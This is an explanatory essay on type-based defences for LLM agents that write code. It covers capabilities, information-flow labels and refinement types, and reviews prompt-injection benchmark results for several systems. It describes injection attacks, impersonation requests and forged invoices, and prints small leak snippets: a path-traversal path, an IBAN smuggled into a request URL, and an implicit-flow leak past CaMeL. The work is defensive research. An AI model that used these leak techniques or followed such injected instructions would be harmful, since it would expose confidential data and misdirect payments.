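The compiler can establish that a piece of code holds the capability for the invoice folder. It can't establish which files the code will open, because a path is just text, and a program may compute it during the run or copy it out of an invoice. To the compiler, `"march.csv"` and `"../payroll/march.csv"` are both values of type `String`. TACIT's library therefore compares each path with the folder as the program runs, and raises an error called `SecurityException` if the path lies outside. Four lines that a model might write show the division of labour:

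```
folder.access("march.csv").read()               compiles and runs
folder.access("../payroll/march.csv").read()    compiles, then fails during the run
payroll.access("march.csv").read()              does not compile: payroll not in scope
() => folder.access("april.csv").read()         does not compile as the block's result
```

For network access, the library compares each address with a list of permitted hosts, as Aver's runtime does.

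These checks happen while the program runs, so they may come after some payments have gone out. They also depend on the library comparing paths correctly, which is easy to get wrong when a path can contain `..` or pass through a link to another folder.

Whoever writes the call to `requestFileSystem` chooses the folder, because the first argument is text. The types don't stop code that can call it from passing `"/payroll"`. TACIT requires a general input-output capability for the call, but it makes one available at the top level of every session, and in the published examples the agents choose the folder themselves. For the invoice program, the company should open the folder in its own code and let the model write only the block.

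### LACUNA: a model fills a gap in a program

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, built a system that works in that way. The group overlaps with the one behind TACIT. In most agents, fixed software calls the model, runs the code it returns and calls it again. In LACUNA, a Scala program calls the model at the point where it needs a result, through one function:

```
def agent[T](task: String): T
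```

The company might write this:

```
requestFileSystem("/invoices"): folder =>
    val total: Int = agent("add up the March invoices in folder")
    total
```

When the program reaches the call to `agent`, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type (`Int`), the surrounding source code with a gap in place of the call, and a list of the available variables with their types. The model returns Scala code, which LACUNA inserts into the gap and compiles with the original program's settings. If the code compiles, it runs in place and its value becomes `total`. Otherwise, LACUNA sends the model the error messages and the model tries again, up to a set number of attempts. If they all fail, the call raises an exception that the company's program can catch.

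The generated code can use whatever is visible at the gap, as if a programmer had typed the code there. A tool is a function in scope. With capture checking on, the capabilities in scope at the gap are the model's permissions. In the example, the code can read the invoice folder, but it can't return a closure that keeps the folder, and it can't pay anyone unless `account` is also visible. To narrow the permissions, a programmer can put the call inside a separate top-level function, where the generated code can use only that function's parameters and the program's global definitions. A few Scala features, such as reflection, would let code act without holding any capability, so Zhao and colleagues recommend a compiler setting that forbids them.

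The generated code can also call `agent` again, for example once per invoice, and LACUNA checks each reply the same way. The types do not prevent these calls from nesting forever, so the runtime has an adjustable limit on their depth.

LACUNA accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, a program has a variable `balance` with the value 100 and asks the model to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an `Int`. The model writes:

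```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces text, not a number, so the compiler rejects the code before it runs and `balance` is still 100. A system that found the error only during the run would already have subtracted 50, and a retry would subtract another 50. If the code called `pay` instead of subtracting, the retry would pay a supplier twice.

This protection covers only errors the compiler can find. If accepted code makes forty payments and then tries to use a path outside the folder, or the bank refuses the forty-first payment, the first forty payments are not reversed.

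### What the LACUNA experiments found

Zhao and colleagues first tested the checker without any model. They wrote roughly 400 cases, each pairing a host program with a piece of code. The code either should run and return a known value or contained a mistake of a kind agents often make. All the cases came out as intended, which is good evidence, though not proof, that the implementation works as designed.

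They then ran LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 hard questions that an agent answers by searching a fixed collection of documents. With the model DeepSeek V4 Flash, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated code. The agent needed 0.7 retries per question on average, and two-thirds of the questions needed none. It answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. The experiment compared only different models inside LACUNA, so it can't support Zhao and colleagues' conclusion that type checking did not reduce accuracy. The 8.6% also doesn't measure how much harm the compiler prevented, because the compiler rejects code for a misspelt variable as well as for using a forbidden file.

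The test on τ²-bench did include a comparison. In this benchmark, an agent handles simulated customer-service conversations, looking up orders and changing bookings. DeepSeek V4 Flash attempted the same 392 tasks with ordinary tool calls and with LACUNA:

| Tasks solved | Tool calls | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% |
| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% |
| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% |
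| All 392 tasks | 90.0% | 76.0% |

LACUNA failed on 24% of the tasks and tool calling on 10%, a difference far too large to be chance with this many tasks. The paper's abstract is therefore wrong to describe this result as "on par" with the baseline agent. The weaker model Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite also did somewhat worse with LACUNA, solving 29.1% of the tasks against 33.2% with tool calling.

Part of the cause seems to be that the models struggled to write Scala. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's code in the retail tasks, where its performance also fell the most. For Gemini, the share of rejected code rose from 3.2% in retail to 89% in telecom. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen much less Scala than Python in training. That can't be the whole explanation, because three other models did slightly better on the retail and airline tasks when they wrote Scala for TACIT than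 when they made tool calls. Zhao and colleagues also chose small, cheap models and switched off their reasoning, so the gap might well disappear with stronger models. For now, the result suggests that checking each action in this way can make an agent a good deal less useful, even though rejected code does no damage.

In the last experiment, Zhao and colleagues tested the capabilities against attackers, using an adapted version of AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks. They gave each agent only the capabilities its task required. Attacks succeeded in 7 of 949 trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 1 of 949 with o4-mini. Across the same two models, one attack in total succeeded against TACIT and one against CaMeL, a system that tracks the origin of each piece of data at run time. These rates are all low, but the comparison has no undefended agent, so it doesn't show how many of the attacks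 the models would have resisted on their own.

Zhao and colleagues note that capabilities do not stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a permission the task needs. The invoice program must hold `account` to pay suppliers. If a forged invoice leads the model to pay a fraudster, the payment uses that same capability, so the compiler accepts it.

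## Pure functions and information flow: using secret data without leaking it

Some suppliers bill in dollars, so suppose the company lets its invoice program contact a public exchange-rate service. The program now holds a capability for the invoice folder, which contains the suppliers' bank details, and a capability called `rates` for the service. It needs both, but together they also allow this:

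```
inv = readInvoices(folder)[0]
fetch(rates, "/usd?ref=" + inv.supplier.iban)
```

The program reads a file it is allowed to read and contacts a host it is allowed to contact, but whoever runs the service receives a supplier's account number. The capture set is `{folder, rates}`, the same as for a version that doesn't leak the number, so the compiler accepts both.

Access control limits which resources code can use, but not where data goes once the code has read it. Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026) point out in *FLOWSH* that a fixed list of hosts can't solve this, because permitting a service is insecure and blocking it is too restrictive. Odersky and colleagues describe a leak that doesn't need a suspicious host. An agent reads a private file that it is allowed to read, then sends the text to the cloud service that runs its language model, as it does with nearly everything it reads.

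### Noninterference

Preventing such leaks means controlling *information flow*, the ways in which data can influence what an observer sees. The standard goal is *noninterference*: changing the secret inputs changes nothing that an outside observer sees. Write P(s, p) for a run of the program P with secret input s and public input p. Then P has noninterference if

```
observed(P(s1, p)) = observed(P(s2, p))     for all s1, s2 and p
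```

The program above fails this test, because a different account number would produce a request for a different address. So does this one:

```
if inv.amount > 10000: fetch(rates, "/usd")
```

The request contains nothing from the invoice, but anyone who sees it arrive learns that the amount is above 10,000. This is an *implicit flow*, and a filter that searches outgoing messages for account numbers would miss it.

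Because the definition compares two runs, watching one run can't confirm that a program satisfies it. Suppose a program sends an ordinary request when an invoice is large and nothing when it is small. Neither run looks suspicious by itself. A type checker has an advantage because it examines both branches of the program.

One way to enforce noninterference is to attach a *label* to each piece of data and pass the label on to everything computed from it. The simplest labels are public and secret. Kim and colleagues also describe labels that list who may read the data. If the accountant and the director may read the invoices, and the director and the auditor may read the contracts, then only the director may read a summary of both.

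Labels can also protect *integrity* by marking data as trusted or untrusted. The goal is then that changing the untrusted inputs does not change the actions that matter. A payment program with this property would make the same payments whatever instructions a supplier had hidden in an invoice.

Full noninterference is often too strict. It forbids showing an outside auditor the invoice program's report, because the total in the report depends on the secret amounts. Practical systems therefore include some way to release chosen data. Language models add another difficulty. *GIF* (2026), a paper on measuring information flow through such models, points out that any token may weakly affect any later token. Once a model has read a secret, everything it writes afterwards has to count as secret, so one solution is to never show the secret to the model that writes the code.

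### A wrapper that accepts only pure functions

TACIT, which Odersky and colleagues released in March 2026, takes this approach. Whoever sets it up marks certain folders as classified, and the library returns the contents of their files in a wrapper called `Classified`. In simplified form:

```
trait Classified[T]:
    def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies a function to the hidden value and wraps the result. The arrow `->` admits only pure functions, which hold no capabilities. The generated code cannot take the value out of the wrapper.

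Suppose that `readInvoices` returns a list in which each invoice has its own wrapper, so the program can tell how many invoices there are but not what they contain. If `inv` is one of them, the compiler judges these lines as follows:

```
val usd = fetch(rates, "/usd")                      accepted
inv.map(i => convert(i.amount, usd))                accepted: result is wrapped
inv.map(i => fetch(rates, i.supplier.iban))         rejected: function uses rates
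if inv.map(i => i.amount > 10000) then
    fetch(rates, "/usd")                            rejected: condition is wrapped
```

The program can fetch the exchange rate and use it inside `map`, because the rate is ordinary data, not a capability. In the third case, the function uses `rates`, so `rates` appears in its capture set and the function isn't pure. The last case is the implicit flow described earlier. The comparison produces a `Classified[Boolean]`, but `if` requires a plain `Boolean`. Moving the `if` inside `map` doesn't help, because the function would then use `rates`, as in the third case.

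Noninterference follows from these rules. The program can use a secret only inside a function that it passes to `map`. That function holds no capabilities, so it can't affect anything outside itself, and its result is wrapped too. The rest of the program therefore behaves the same whatever the secret is, except that the secret may affect timing or whether the program finishes, which TACIT doesn't control.

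The library also has to block some less obvious leaks. A function inside `map` might open a folder and write the secret there, so `requestFileSystem` requires an input-output capability, which a pure function can't hold. The function might also throw an exception with an account number in the error message, so TACIT catches exceptions and hides the failure along with the value. The drawback is that a mistake inside `map` can look like success, with no error message and an empty result.

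A payment is an effect, so the program can't call the ordinary `pay` inside `map` either. The company has to write a version that takes wrapped arguments, just as TACIT has a function that writes wrapped text to a classified file:

```
def pay(account: Account^, supplier: Classified[Supplier],
        amount: Classified[Int]): Unit

for inv <- readInvoices(folder) do
    pay(account, inv.map(_.supplier), inv.map(_.amount))
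```

The company's own code behind `pay` unwraps the details and sends them to the bank. The generated program can pass a supplier's account number to `pay`, but it can't send the number to the exchange-rate service, even though it holds the capability to contact that service.

### A second model and a second screen

A model that never reads the invoices can't detect that one of them is marked "disputed". TACIT therefore lets the program call a separate, trusted model, for instance one on the company's own computers. The function for this, `chat`, takes wrapped text and returns a wrapped answer. The trusted model has no tools, so instructions hidden in an invoice might distort its answer but couldn't make it send anything. In 2023, Simon Willison proposed this division between a model that acts and a model that reads untrusted data, and called it the dual-LLM pattern.

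The compiler treats `chat` as holding no capabilities, so a program may use it on secrets. But `chat` sends those secrets to a trusted model, which is a separate piece of software. Odersky and colleagues say that whoever runs the system must ensure the model retains none of the data it receives, because the types can't check that.

The user still needs to see the results. When generated code prints something, TACIT normally shows it to both the user and the cloud model. If the value is wrapped, the model receives only `Classified(****)`, while a separate channel displays the real content on the user's screen. In one example, a user asks for a summary of a secret contract and reads the summary. The user then asks how long it is, and the cloud model writes code to compute the length but sees neither the summary nor the number.

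### Testing TACIT for leaks

Odersky and colleagues tested the wrapper on a software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, some of which contained ready-made code for reading the secrets. That made 120 trials. In another 11, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to be someone with a right to them, such as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, with and without the wrapper. The table shows how often no secret appeared in the agent's output:

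| Trials | With wrapper | Without wrapper |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| MiniMax M2.5, 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |

Overall, 98.5% of Claude's trials and 91.6% of MiniMax's were free of leaks without the wrapper. The injections were a weak test, because the models resisted 237 of 240 without it. The malicious requests are better evidence, since 10 of 22 succeeded without the wrapper and none with it.

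All the attacks were fixed in advance, and nobody adapted them after studying TACIT. A serious attacker would look for a flaw in the compiler or the library instead of inventing a more persuasive story. The project's public documentation, lampepfl's *TACIT*, describes a version that blocked dangerous language features by searching the code for forbidden patterns, which can miss unusual ways of writing the same thing. The trials mostly show that the implementation has no obvious holes, so the main reason to trust the wrapper is the argument from its types.

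The wrapper didn't stop the agents from doing useful work on this project. They used the trusted model to summarise a confidential incident report and remove names from employee reviews. Claude completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Claude scored lower without the wrapper because it ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection, so the wrapper probably isn't the reason for the difference.

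They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, the benchmark of prompt injections that Zhao and colleagues adapted for LACUNA. Across two models and 963 attacks on each, one attack counted as successful. A user had asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and the reviews contained an attacker's recommendation for a different one. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the planted recommendation. AgentDojo counts this attack as successful if the output contains the name of the attacker's hotel. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, and the attacker gained no booking, so this seems to be a fault in the scoring.

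The AgentDojo results may be weak evidence about pure functions. In the banking tasks, bills arrive wrapped, but the function that sends money takes an ordinary string as the recipient. The agent's instructions also mention side effects inside functions passed to `map`, so it is unclear whether this version of TACIT prevented such functions from making payments.

CaMeL, which tracks the origin of data at run time, completed a larger share of tasks than TACIT in six of the eight combinations of model and domain that Odersky and colleagues report. They nevertheless describe the two systems' completion rates as comparable. With o4-mini, CaMeL completed 81.4% of the office tasks and TACIT 52.9%. The big exception was travel with Gemini 2.5 Pro, where CaMeL completed 1.4% and TACIT 64.3%.

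### What writing Scala cost the agents

Two further benchmarks compared agents that wrote Scala for TACIT with agents that made ordinary tool calls. Scores on τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, are averages over ten runs per task. SWE-bench Lite consists of 300 real software repairs, and only MiniMax was tested on it.

| Tasks solved | Tool calls | TACIT |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b, airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
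| gpt-oss-120b, retail | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, retail | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, retail | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

TACIT was slightly ahead in all six customer-service comparisons but solved five fewer of the software repairs. Few programs needed a second attempt, from 0.32% for gpt-oss-120b in retail to 7.93% for DeepSeek in airline, and those programs took 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Compiling a program usually took less than a second.

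This is good evidence that models can write Scala that passes the capability checks. But the customer-service functions return customers' names, addresses and orders without a wrapper, so it isn't evidence that models can work with secrets they can't read. An agent that had to handle a complaint without seeing the customer's order would presumably do worse.

### Letting only trusted data into a payment

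The wrapper protects secrets, but a system must also keep out bad data, such as a forged invoice. Zhou and colleagues use ELBA, their Haskell system for language-based agent control, to show how types can do this. As in the calculator example, the developer chooses the type that the model's program must have.

Their example is an agent that compiles a bibliography. Every entry has to come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers, because language models sometimes invent references. The developer provides three functions, roughly like this:

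```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A `DOI` identifies a paper, and a `Bib` is its bibliography entry. The model's program must have the type `BibIO ()`, a restricted type like `RIO`. It can therefore write to files only through `appendToBibFile`, which accepts only a `Trusted Bib`. The library keeps the constructor of `Trusted` private, so the program can get a `Trusted Bib` only by fetching it from DBLP. It can still search, sort and filter the entries freely.

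Zhou and colleagues gave 100 bibliography tasks to ELBA and to an ordinary agent with a web search tool, both using Claude Sonnet 5. They counted a citation as invented if its authors, year or DOI was wrong. The ordinary agent invented 19 of its 1,002 citations, and ELBA invented none of its 925. The agents also drew on different sources, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the types. `Trusted` guarantees only where an entry came from, so the program could still cite a real paper that has nothing to do with the topic.

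The company can use the same method for payments. It keeps a register of approved suppliers and provides a function that looks up a name and returns a `Trusted Supplier` containing the bank details from the register. If `pay` accepts only this type, the compiler will reject a program that tries to pay an account number copied from an invoice. A fraudster who sends an invoice in a real supplier's name can still trigger a payment to that supplier, but can't redirect the money.

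### Labels that rise as the program reads

When a policy depends on what the program has already read, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library. LIO gives the running program a *current label*, which records how secret and how trustworthy its data is. Each time the program reads something, LIO updates the label to account for the source. Before each write, LIO compares the label with what the destination allows.

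In Zhou and colleagues' example, a program fetches a page from an untrusted website and then tries to pass the content to the user through a function that requires trusted data. LIO stops the program at the second step. The invoice program would have similar trouble:

```
invs = readInvoices(folder)      label: influenced by suppliers
pay(account, supplier, amount)   requires: influenced only by the company
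                                 -> the run stops
```

LIO makes these comparisons at run time, not in the type checker. Its type `DC ()` guarantees only that every effect passes through LIO's functions, so the generated code can't skip the comparison. But as with TACIT's path checks, the comparison may come after some payments have gone out.

The label also rises more easily than it falls. One untrusted invoice could block every later payment, even unrelated ones. LIO contains this problem with a function called `toLabeled`, which runs part of the program separately, lets the label rise there, and returns the result in a sealed value with its own label. The main program's label stays the same as long as the program doesn't open the sealed value.

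An agent that has to write a message based on untrusted web pages can have a subagent read the pages and write the message inside `toLabeled`. The agent then gives the sealed message to a function that checks whether the message's label is acceptable for the recipient. In ELBA, the subagent can use tools as long as its label permits each action, whereas the model that reads untrusted data in the usual dual-LLM pattern has no tools.

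### Attacks on an agent that always obeys

Zhou and colleagues tested the labels on the part of AgentDojo that simulates Slack, a workplace messaging service. It has 105 pairs, combining each of 21 user tasks with each of 5 attacks. At first the test couldn't show whether the labels worked, because every attack failed against all four models even with the labels switched off.

So the researchers simulated a worst case. Whenever a subagent received data with the marker that AgentDojo uses for its injections, they deleted the subagent's real task and left only the data, including the attacker's instructions. They ran the 105 pairs seven times for each model, a total of 735 runs with the policy and 735 without it:

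| Model | Attacks resisted, with policy | Attacks resisted, without | Tasks completed, with policy | Tasks completed, without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

Up to 42% of the attacks succeeded without the policy and none succeeded with it, although the count of zero involves some judgement. AgentDojo's automatic scoring marked 29 of the 2,940 protected runs as successful attacks because the agent visited a web address that the attacker had named. Zhou and colleagues examined all 29 and concluded that visiting the fixed address had leaked nothing.

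This is a more demanding test than TACIT's because it doesn't depend on the model recognising an attack. But it uses only five different attacks, each repeated seven times. Better wording wouldn't help an attacker, because the subagent already obeys. An attacker would need to find a harmful action that the policy permits or a mistake in the trusted code, and nobody in this experiment was looking for either.

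Agents completed between 33% and 44% fewer tasks with the policy than without it. Many of these failures occurred because the policy blocked legitimate actions, such as acting on the contents of a web page that the user had asked about. Even without an attack, the models completed only 8 to 10 of the 21 tasks with the policy, compared with 14 to 18 without it. Type errors were a small part of the problem, since ELBA needed about 0.13 retries per run and gave up on 7 of 2,688 runs.

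A company might accept these losses if a person could approve the refused actions. Kim and colleagues tested this kind of arrangement with FLOWSH, which labels files and network data while an agent runs shell commands and asks the user for approval only when an action would break the policy. They compared it with a permissive sandbox that asked about every action it couldn't guarantee to be safe. On office tasks, FLOWSH needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed task, but the agent's completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower.

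### CaMeL and the LLMbda calculus

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, relies more on the order of events. One model writes the whole program from the user's request before it reads any untrusted data, so an invoice, for example, can't influence which program runs. A second model, which has no tools, extracts values from the data, and CaMeL's interpreter tracks their labels at run time. According to Odersky and colleagues, CaMeL programs can't define their own functions, and an agent can't change its plan after reading something unexpected. Zhou and colleagues found that CaMeL completed 4 to 6 of the 21 Slack tasks with its policies on, about half as many as ELBA, though ELBA took roughly three times as long and used different policies.

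Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, also found a leak in CaMeL's label tracking. A program of this form shows how it works:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: sendEmail(outsider, "rich")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips `rich = False`. CaMeL's interpreter can't label an assignment that never runs, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email, so the outsider learns whether the balance is high. In TACIT, the first `if` would not compile with a classified balance, because its condition would be wrapped.

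The LLMbda calculus is a small, untyped programming language for agents. Like CaMeL, it tracks labels at run time, but it stops a program that tries to change public state inside a branch that depends on a secret. Garby and colleagues proved that every program in the language satisfies a form of noninterference, including programs that a model writes during the run, and checked the proof by computer. This form of noninterference allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes.

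On AgentDojo's banking tasks, Garby and colleagues' agent resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. Without attacks, it completed between 65% and 75% of the tasks, depending on the model, while CaMeL with its policies on completed 37.5%. The agent's generated code could *endorse* data, which means relabelling untrusted data as trusted. Without this option, the completion rate fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 65% to 54% with another. Their proof guarantees that endorsing data can't leak a secret, but not that the endorsed data is harmless. The invoice program would need to endorse the amounts it pays, because they come from documents that the suppliers wrote.

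## Refinement types: limiting which values an action may be given

If `pay` accepts only a `Trusted Supplier`, a forged invoice can't send money to a new account, but it can still ask for too much. The program copies the amount from a document that the supplier wrote, and the type of the amount, `Int`, allows every integer. A refinement type allows fewer. It has the form

```
{x : B | p(x)}
```

and contains the values x of an ordinary type B for which the condition p is true. For example, `{x : Int | x > 0}` is the type of positive integers.

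*First-Class Refinement Types for Scala* (Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky, 2026) traces the idea back at least to Robert Cartwright's work in 1976. It became more practical in 2008, when Patrick Rondon and colleagues introduced *liquid types*. These restrict the conditions to kinds of logic that an SMT solver can decide, and the checker infers many of the conditions.

### Subtyping as implication

A checker compares two refinement types by asking whether one condition implies the other:

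```
{x : B | p}  is a subtype of  {x : B | q}
    if, for every x in B,  p(x) implies q(x)
```

Every integer above 1 is also above 0, so a function that requires a positive integer accepts a value of type `{x : Int | x > 1}`. A function that requires an integer above 1 does not accept a value typed only as a positive integer, because that value could be 1. *Refinement-Types Driven Development* (Domínguez and Spiwack, 2025) compares this relationship to subsets in set theory.

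The checker also uses what it knows from the surrounding code. Gamboa, Reese and colleagues (2025), in *Usability Barriers for Liquid Types*, give the example of a function that returns n if n is positive and −n otherwise, and promises a result of at least 0. In the second branch the checker knows that n is not positive, so it sends the solver this formula:

```
for all n:  not (n > 0)  implies  -n >= 0
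```

Such a formula is called a *verification condition*. The solver searches for a value of n that makes it false. The branch passes if there is no such value, but if the solver finds one, the checker rejects the program.

### A limit on one payment

Suppose the company gives `pay` this signature:

```
pay : (supplier : Trusted Supplier,
       amount   : {a : Int | 0 < a and a <= approved})  →  ()
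```

Here `approved` is the maximum allowed total of this month's payments, in cents. The company's code sets it, and the generated program can't change it.

The original invoice program now fails the check. It calls `pay` with `inv.amount`, about which the checker knows nothing, and the amount might be zero. To pass, a program has to test the amount first. Suppose that the invoices offer a discount for early payment and the model writes this:

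```
for inv in invoices:
    if inv.amount <= approved and 0 <= inv.discount and inv.discount < inv.amount:
        pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount - inv.discount)
```

Write a for the amount, d for the discount and L for the approved limit. The call happens only if the test succeeds, so the checker may assume the three parts of the test. The solver receives:

```
for all a, d, L:
    (a <= L  and  0 <= d  and  d < a)
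        implies  (0 < a - d  and  a - d <= L)
```

It looks for a counterexample, which would be three integers that satisfy all of these:

```
a <= L,    0 <= d,    d < a,    and  (a - d <= 0  or  a - d > L)
```

There are none. The difference is positive because d is less than a. It is at most a because d is not negative, and a is at most L. The checker therefore accepts the program.

Suppose the model leaves out `0 <= inv.discount`. The solver finds a = 100, d = −50 and L = 100, for which the program would pay 150, so the checker rejects the program. Running it on fifty folders of ordinary invoices would not have exposed this mistake, because honest suppliers don't offer negative discounts, though a dishonest one might.

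The signature limits the damage from a wrong amount but doesn't ensure that the amount is right. If the program mixes up cents and euros and pays a hundred times too much, the payment still passes as long as it is below the limit. The company can do better by letting the condition refer to another argument. If `pay` also takes the purchase order, its type can require `a <= order.total`.

### A limit on all payments together

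Two hundred payments can each be below `approved` and still total almost two hundred times `approved`. A refinement on `amount` can't prevent this because it restricts only the value passed in each call. A cumulative limit needs a condition on the program's history, including earlier calls.

F* is a language for writing programs together with proofs about them. It can attach to an effect a *precondition*, which must be true before the action, and a *postcondition*, which will be true afterwards. *Securing Verified IO Programs Against Unverified Code in F\** (Andrici, Ciobâcă and colleagues, 2023) uses these to describe input and output. Each operation adds an event to a *trace*, recording the operation's arguments and result. A precondition can refer to earlier events in the trace, for example to require that a file is still open. A postcondition can also describe the events that the function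 added.

In simplified notation, the payment limit becomes:

```
pay : (supplier : Trusted Supplier, amount : Int)  →  IO ()
    requires   0 < amount  and  paid(h) + amount <= approved
    ensures    new events = [Payment(supplier, amount)]
```

The letter h stands for the trace before the call, and `paid` adds up the payments in it:

```
paid(empty trace)            = 0
paid(h, then Payment(s, a))  = paid(h) + a
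paid(h, then another event)  = paid(h)
```

The original program already kept a running total, although it used the total only for the report. A version that passes the check compares the total with the limit before each payment:

```
total = 0
for inv in invoices:
    if inv.amount > 0 and total + inv.amount <= approved:
        pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount)
        total = total + inv.amount
```

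The checker can't go through the loop round by round, because it doesn't know how many invoices there will be. It needs a *loop invariant*, a statement that is true before the loop starts and stays true after every round. Here the invariant is `paid(h) = total`, and the checker has to establish three things:

1. Before the loop, the program has paid nothing and `total` is 0, so the invariant is true.
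2. At each call, the precondition of `pay` follows from the invariant and the test:

```
(paid(h) = total  and  amount > 0  and  total + amount <= approved)
    implies  (0 < amount  and  paid(h) + amount <= approved)
```

3. After each payment, both `paid(h)` and `total` have grown by `amount`, so they are still equal. If the program skips an invoice, neither changes.

The solver can do all of this by replacing `paid(h)` with `total`. The only other fact it needs about `paid` is that each payment increases it by the amount of that payment.

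A common mistake is to test `total <= approved` instead, which leaves out the next payment. The solver then finds a counterexample with a total of 900, a next payment of 200 and a limit of 1,000. The program would pay 1,100 in total, so the checker rejects it.

### Guarding verified code against unverified code

The company may not want to depend on the model finding an invariant. It could verify only its own code, including `pay`, and let the model write ordinary code without proofs. But compilers for languages like F* usually erase preconditions after checking them, so unverified code could then call `pay` with any amount.

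Andrici, Ciobâcă and colleagues built SCIO* to restore the lost conditions as run-time checks. Their main example is a web server that is verified to answer every request but passes each one to an unverified handler. The server's proof assumes that the handler will either answer the client or return an error. A hostile handler could report success without answering. SCIO* therefore wraps the handler in a check that searches the trace when the handler returns. If the trace contains no answer, the check turns the result into an error, and the server sends the client an error message.

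That check would come too late for a handler that reads the password file. SCIO* therefore has a monitor, which tests each of the handler's operations before it runs and blocks any attempt to open a file outside one folder. The verified server's own operations need no such checks. Andrici and colleagues proved in F* that the server and any handler together behave as promised. The proof assumes that the handler is also written in a subset of F* and that its only side effects are input and output, so it doesn't yet cover a handler in Python.

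For the invoice program, the wrapper around `pay` would test `0 < amount` and `paid(h) + amount <= approved` on each call from the generated code. The wrapper wouldn't have to store the whole trace, because SCIO* lets the developer keep a summary, which here is one running total. The generated code would need no proof, but as with TACIT's path checks, the wrapper might refuse a call after some payments had gone out.

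*Misquoted No More* (Andrici, Pribisova and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up, applies the idea to AI agents. A small verified wrapper reads a file, lets an unverified agent work on it, reads the file again, and reports success only if the new contents pass a test. This suits tasks whose results are easier to check than to produce. In the published example, the wrapper reports a failure but doesn't restore the old file, so a company couldn't use it in this form for payments, which are hard to reverse.

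### Liquid Haskell, Flux and Scala

Few programmers use F*, so several projects have added refinement types to more familiar languages. Gamboa and colleagues call Liquid Haskell the most mature implementation of liquid types. It is a plugin for the Haskell compiler that reads refined signatures from specially marked comments and sends the resulting formulas to an SMT solver.

Liquid Haskell also accepts signatures that begin with `assume` without checking them. Programmers need these for outside libraries, and Domínguez and Spiwack advise them to justify each one, because a false assumption can let through anything from a wrong result to a security hole. A model allowed to write `assume` can declare any amount to be within the limit, so the company has to forbid `assume` in generated code and write all signatures that use it itself.

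Domínguez and Spiwack also needed to enforce a rule that Liquid Haskell's logic does not naturally express, because it concerned the order of a program's actions. They enforced it by hiding a type behind a function that always performs the required test, much as ELBA hides the constructor of `Trusted`. A company using Liquid Haskell could limit each payment with a refinement and check the cumulative limit inside such a function.

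Flux adds refinement types to Rust, a language in which programs often change values in place. If a program tests an amount and another part of the program then changes it, the result of the test may not hold for the new amount, a problem that Haskell largely avoids. Rust's ownership rules already determine which code may change a value at any moment. As Bovel and colleagues explain, Flux lets code that exclusively owns a value give it a new refinement, while code that has only borrowed the value must preserve the old one.

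Bovel and colleagues added refinement types to the Scala compiler. A programmer writes `Int with x > 0` as an ordinary type, without special comments or a separate tool. On small test programs, the checks added at most about 12% to compilation time, compared with at least 56% for Stainless, an existing verifier for Scala. Scala is also the language of TACIT and LACUNA, so one compiler might eventually check both which account a program can use and how much it can pay.

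The prototype isn't ready for that. To keep the compiler fast and self-contained, Bovel and colleagues wrote a solver of about 600 lines instead of using an SMT solver. Their solver has no complete method even for *linear arithmetic*, in which a formula may add and compare unknown numbers but multiply them only by constants. The prototype would probably reject the discount program above, although the program is safe. The programmer can then add `.runtimeChecked`, which tests the condition at run time and throws an exception if it is false. More seriously for untrusted code, the prototype assumes, without checking, that every function used in a condition is pure. Bovel and colleagues suggest using capture checking to verify this, but haven't yet done so.

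### Questions a solver can't settle

A checker that can't prove a condition has to either reject the program or test the condition at run time. How often a proof fails depends on what the condition is about.

If the program converts dollars to euros, it multiplies an unknown amount by an unknown rate. Formulas with products of unknown integers are much harder to solve than linear ones, and mathematicians showed in 1970 that no procedure can settle all of them. *Practical Range Refinement Types with Inference* (Aebi and Furia, 2026) keeps its checker fast by sending the solver only linear formulas about individual values. The invoice program can avoid the problem by storing the converted amount in a variable and testing that variable against `approved`, because the solver then needs no information about how the amount was calculated.

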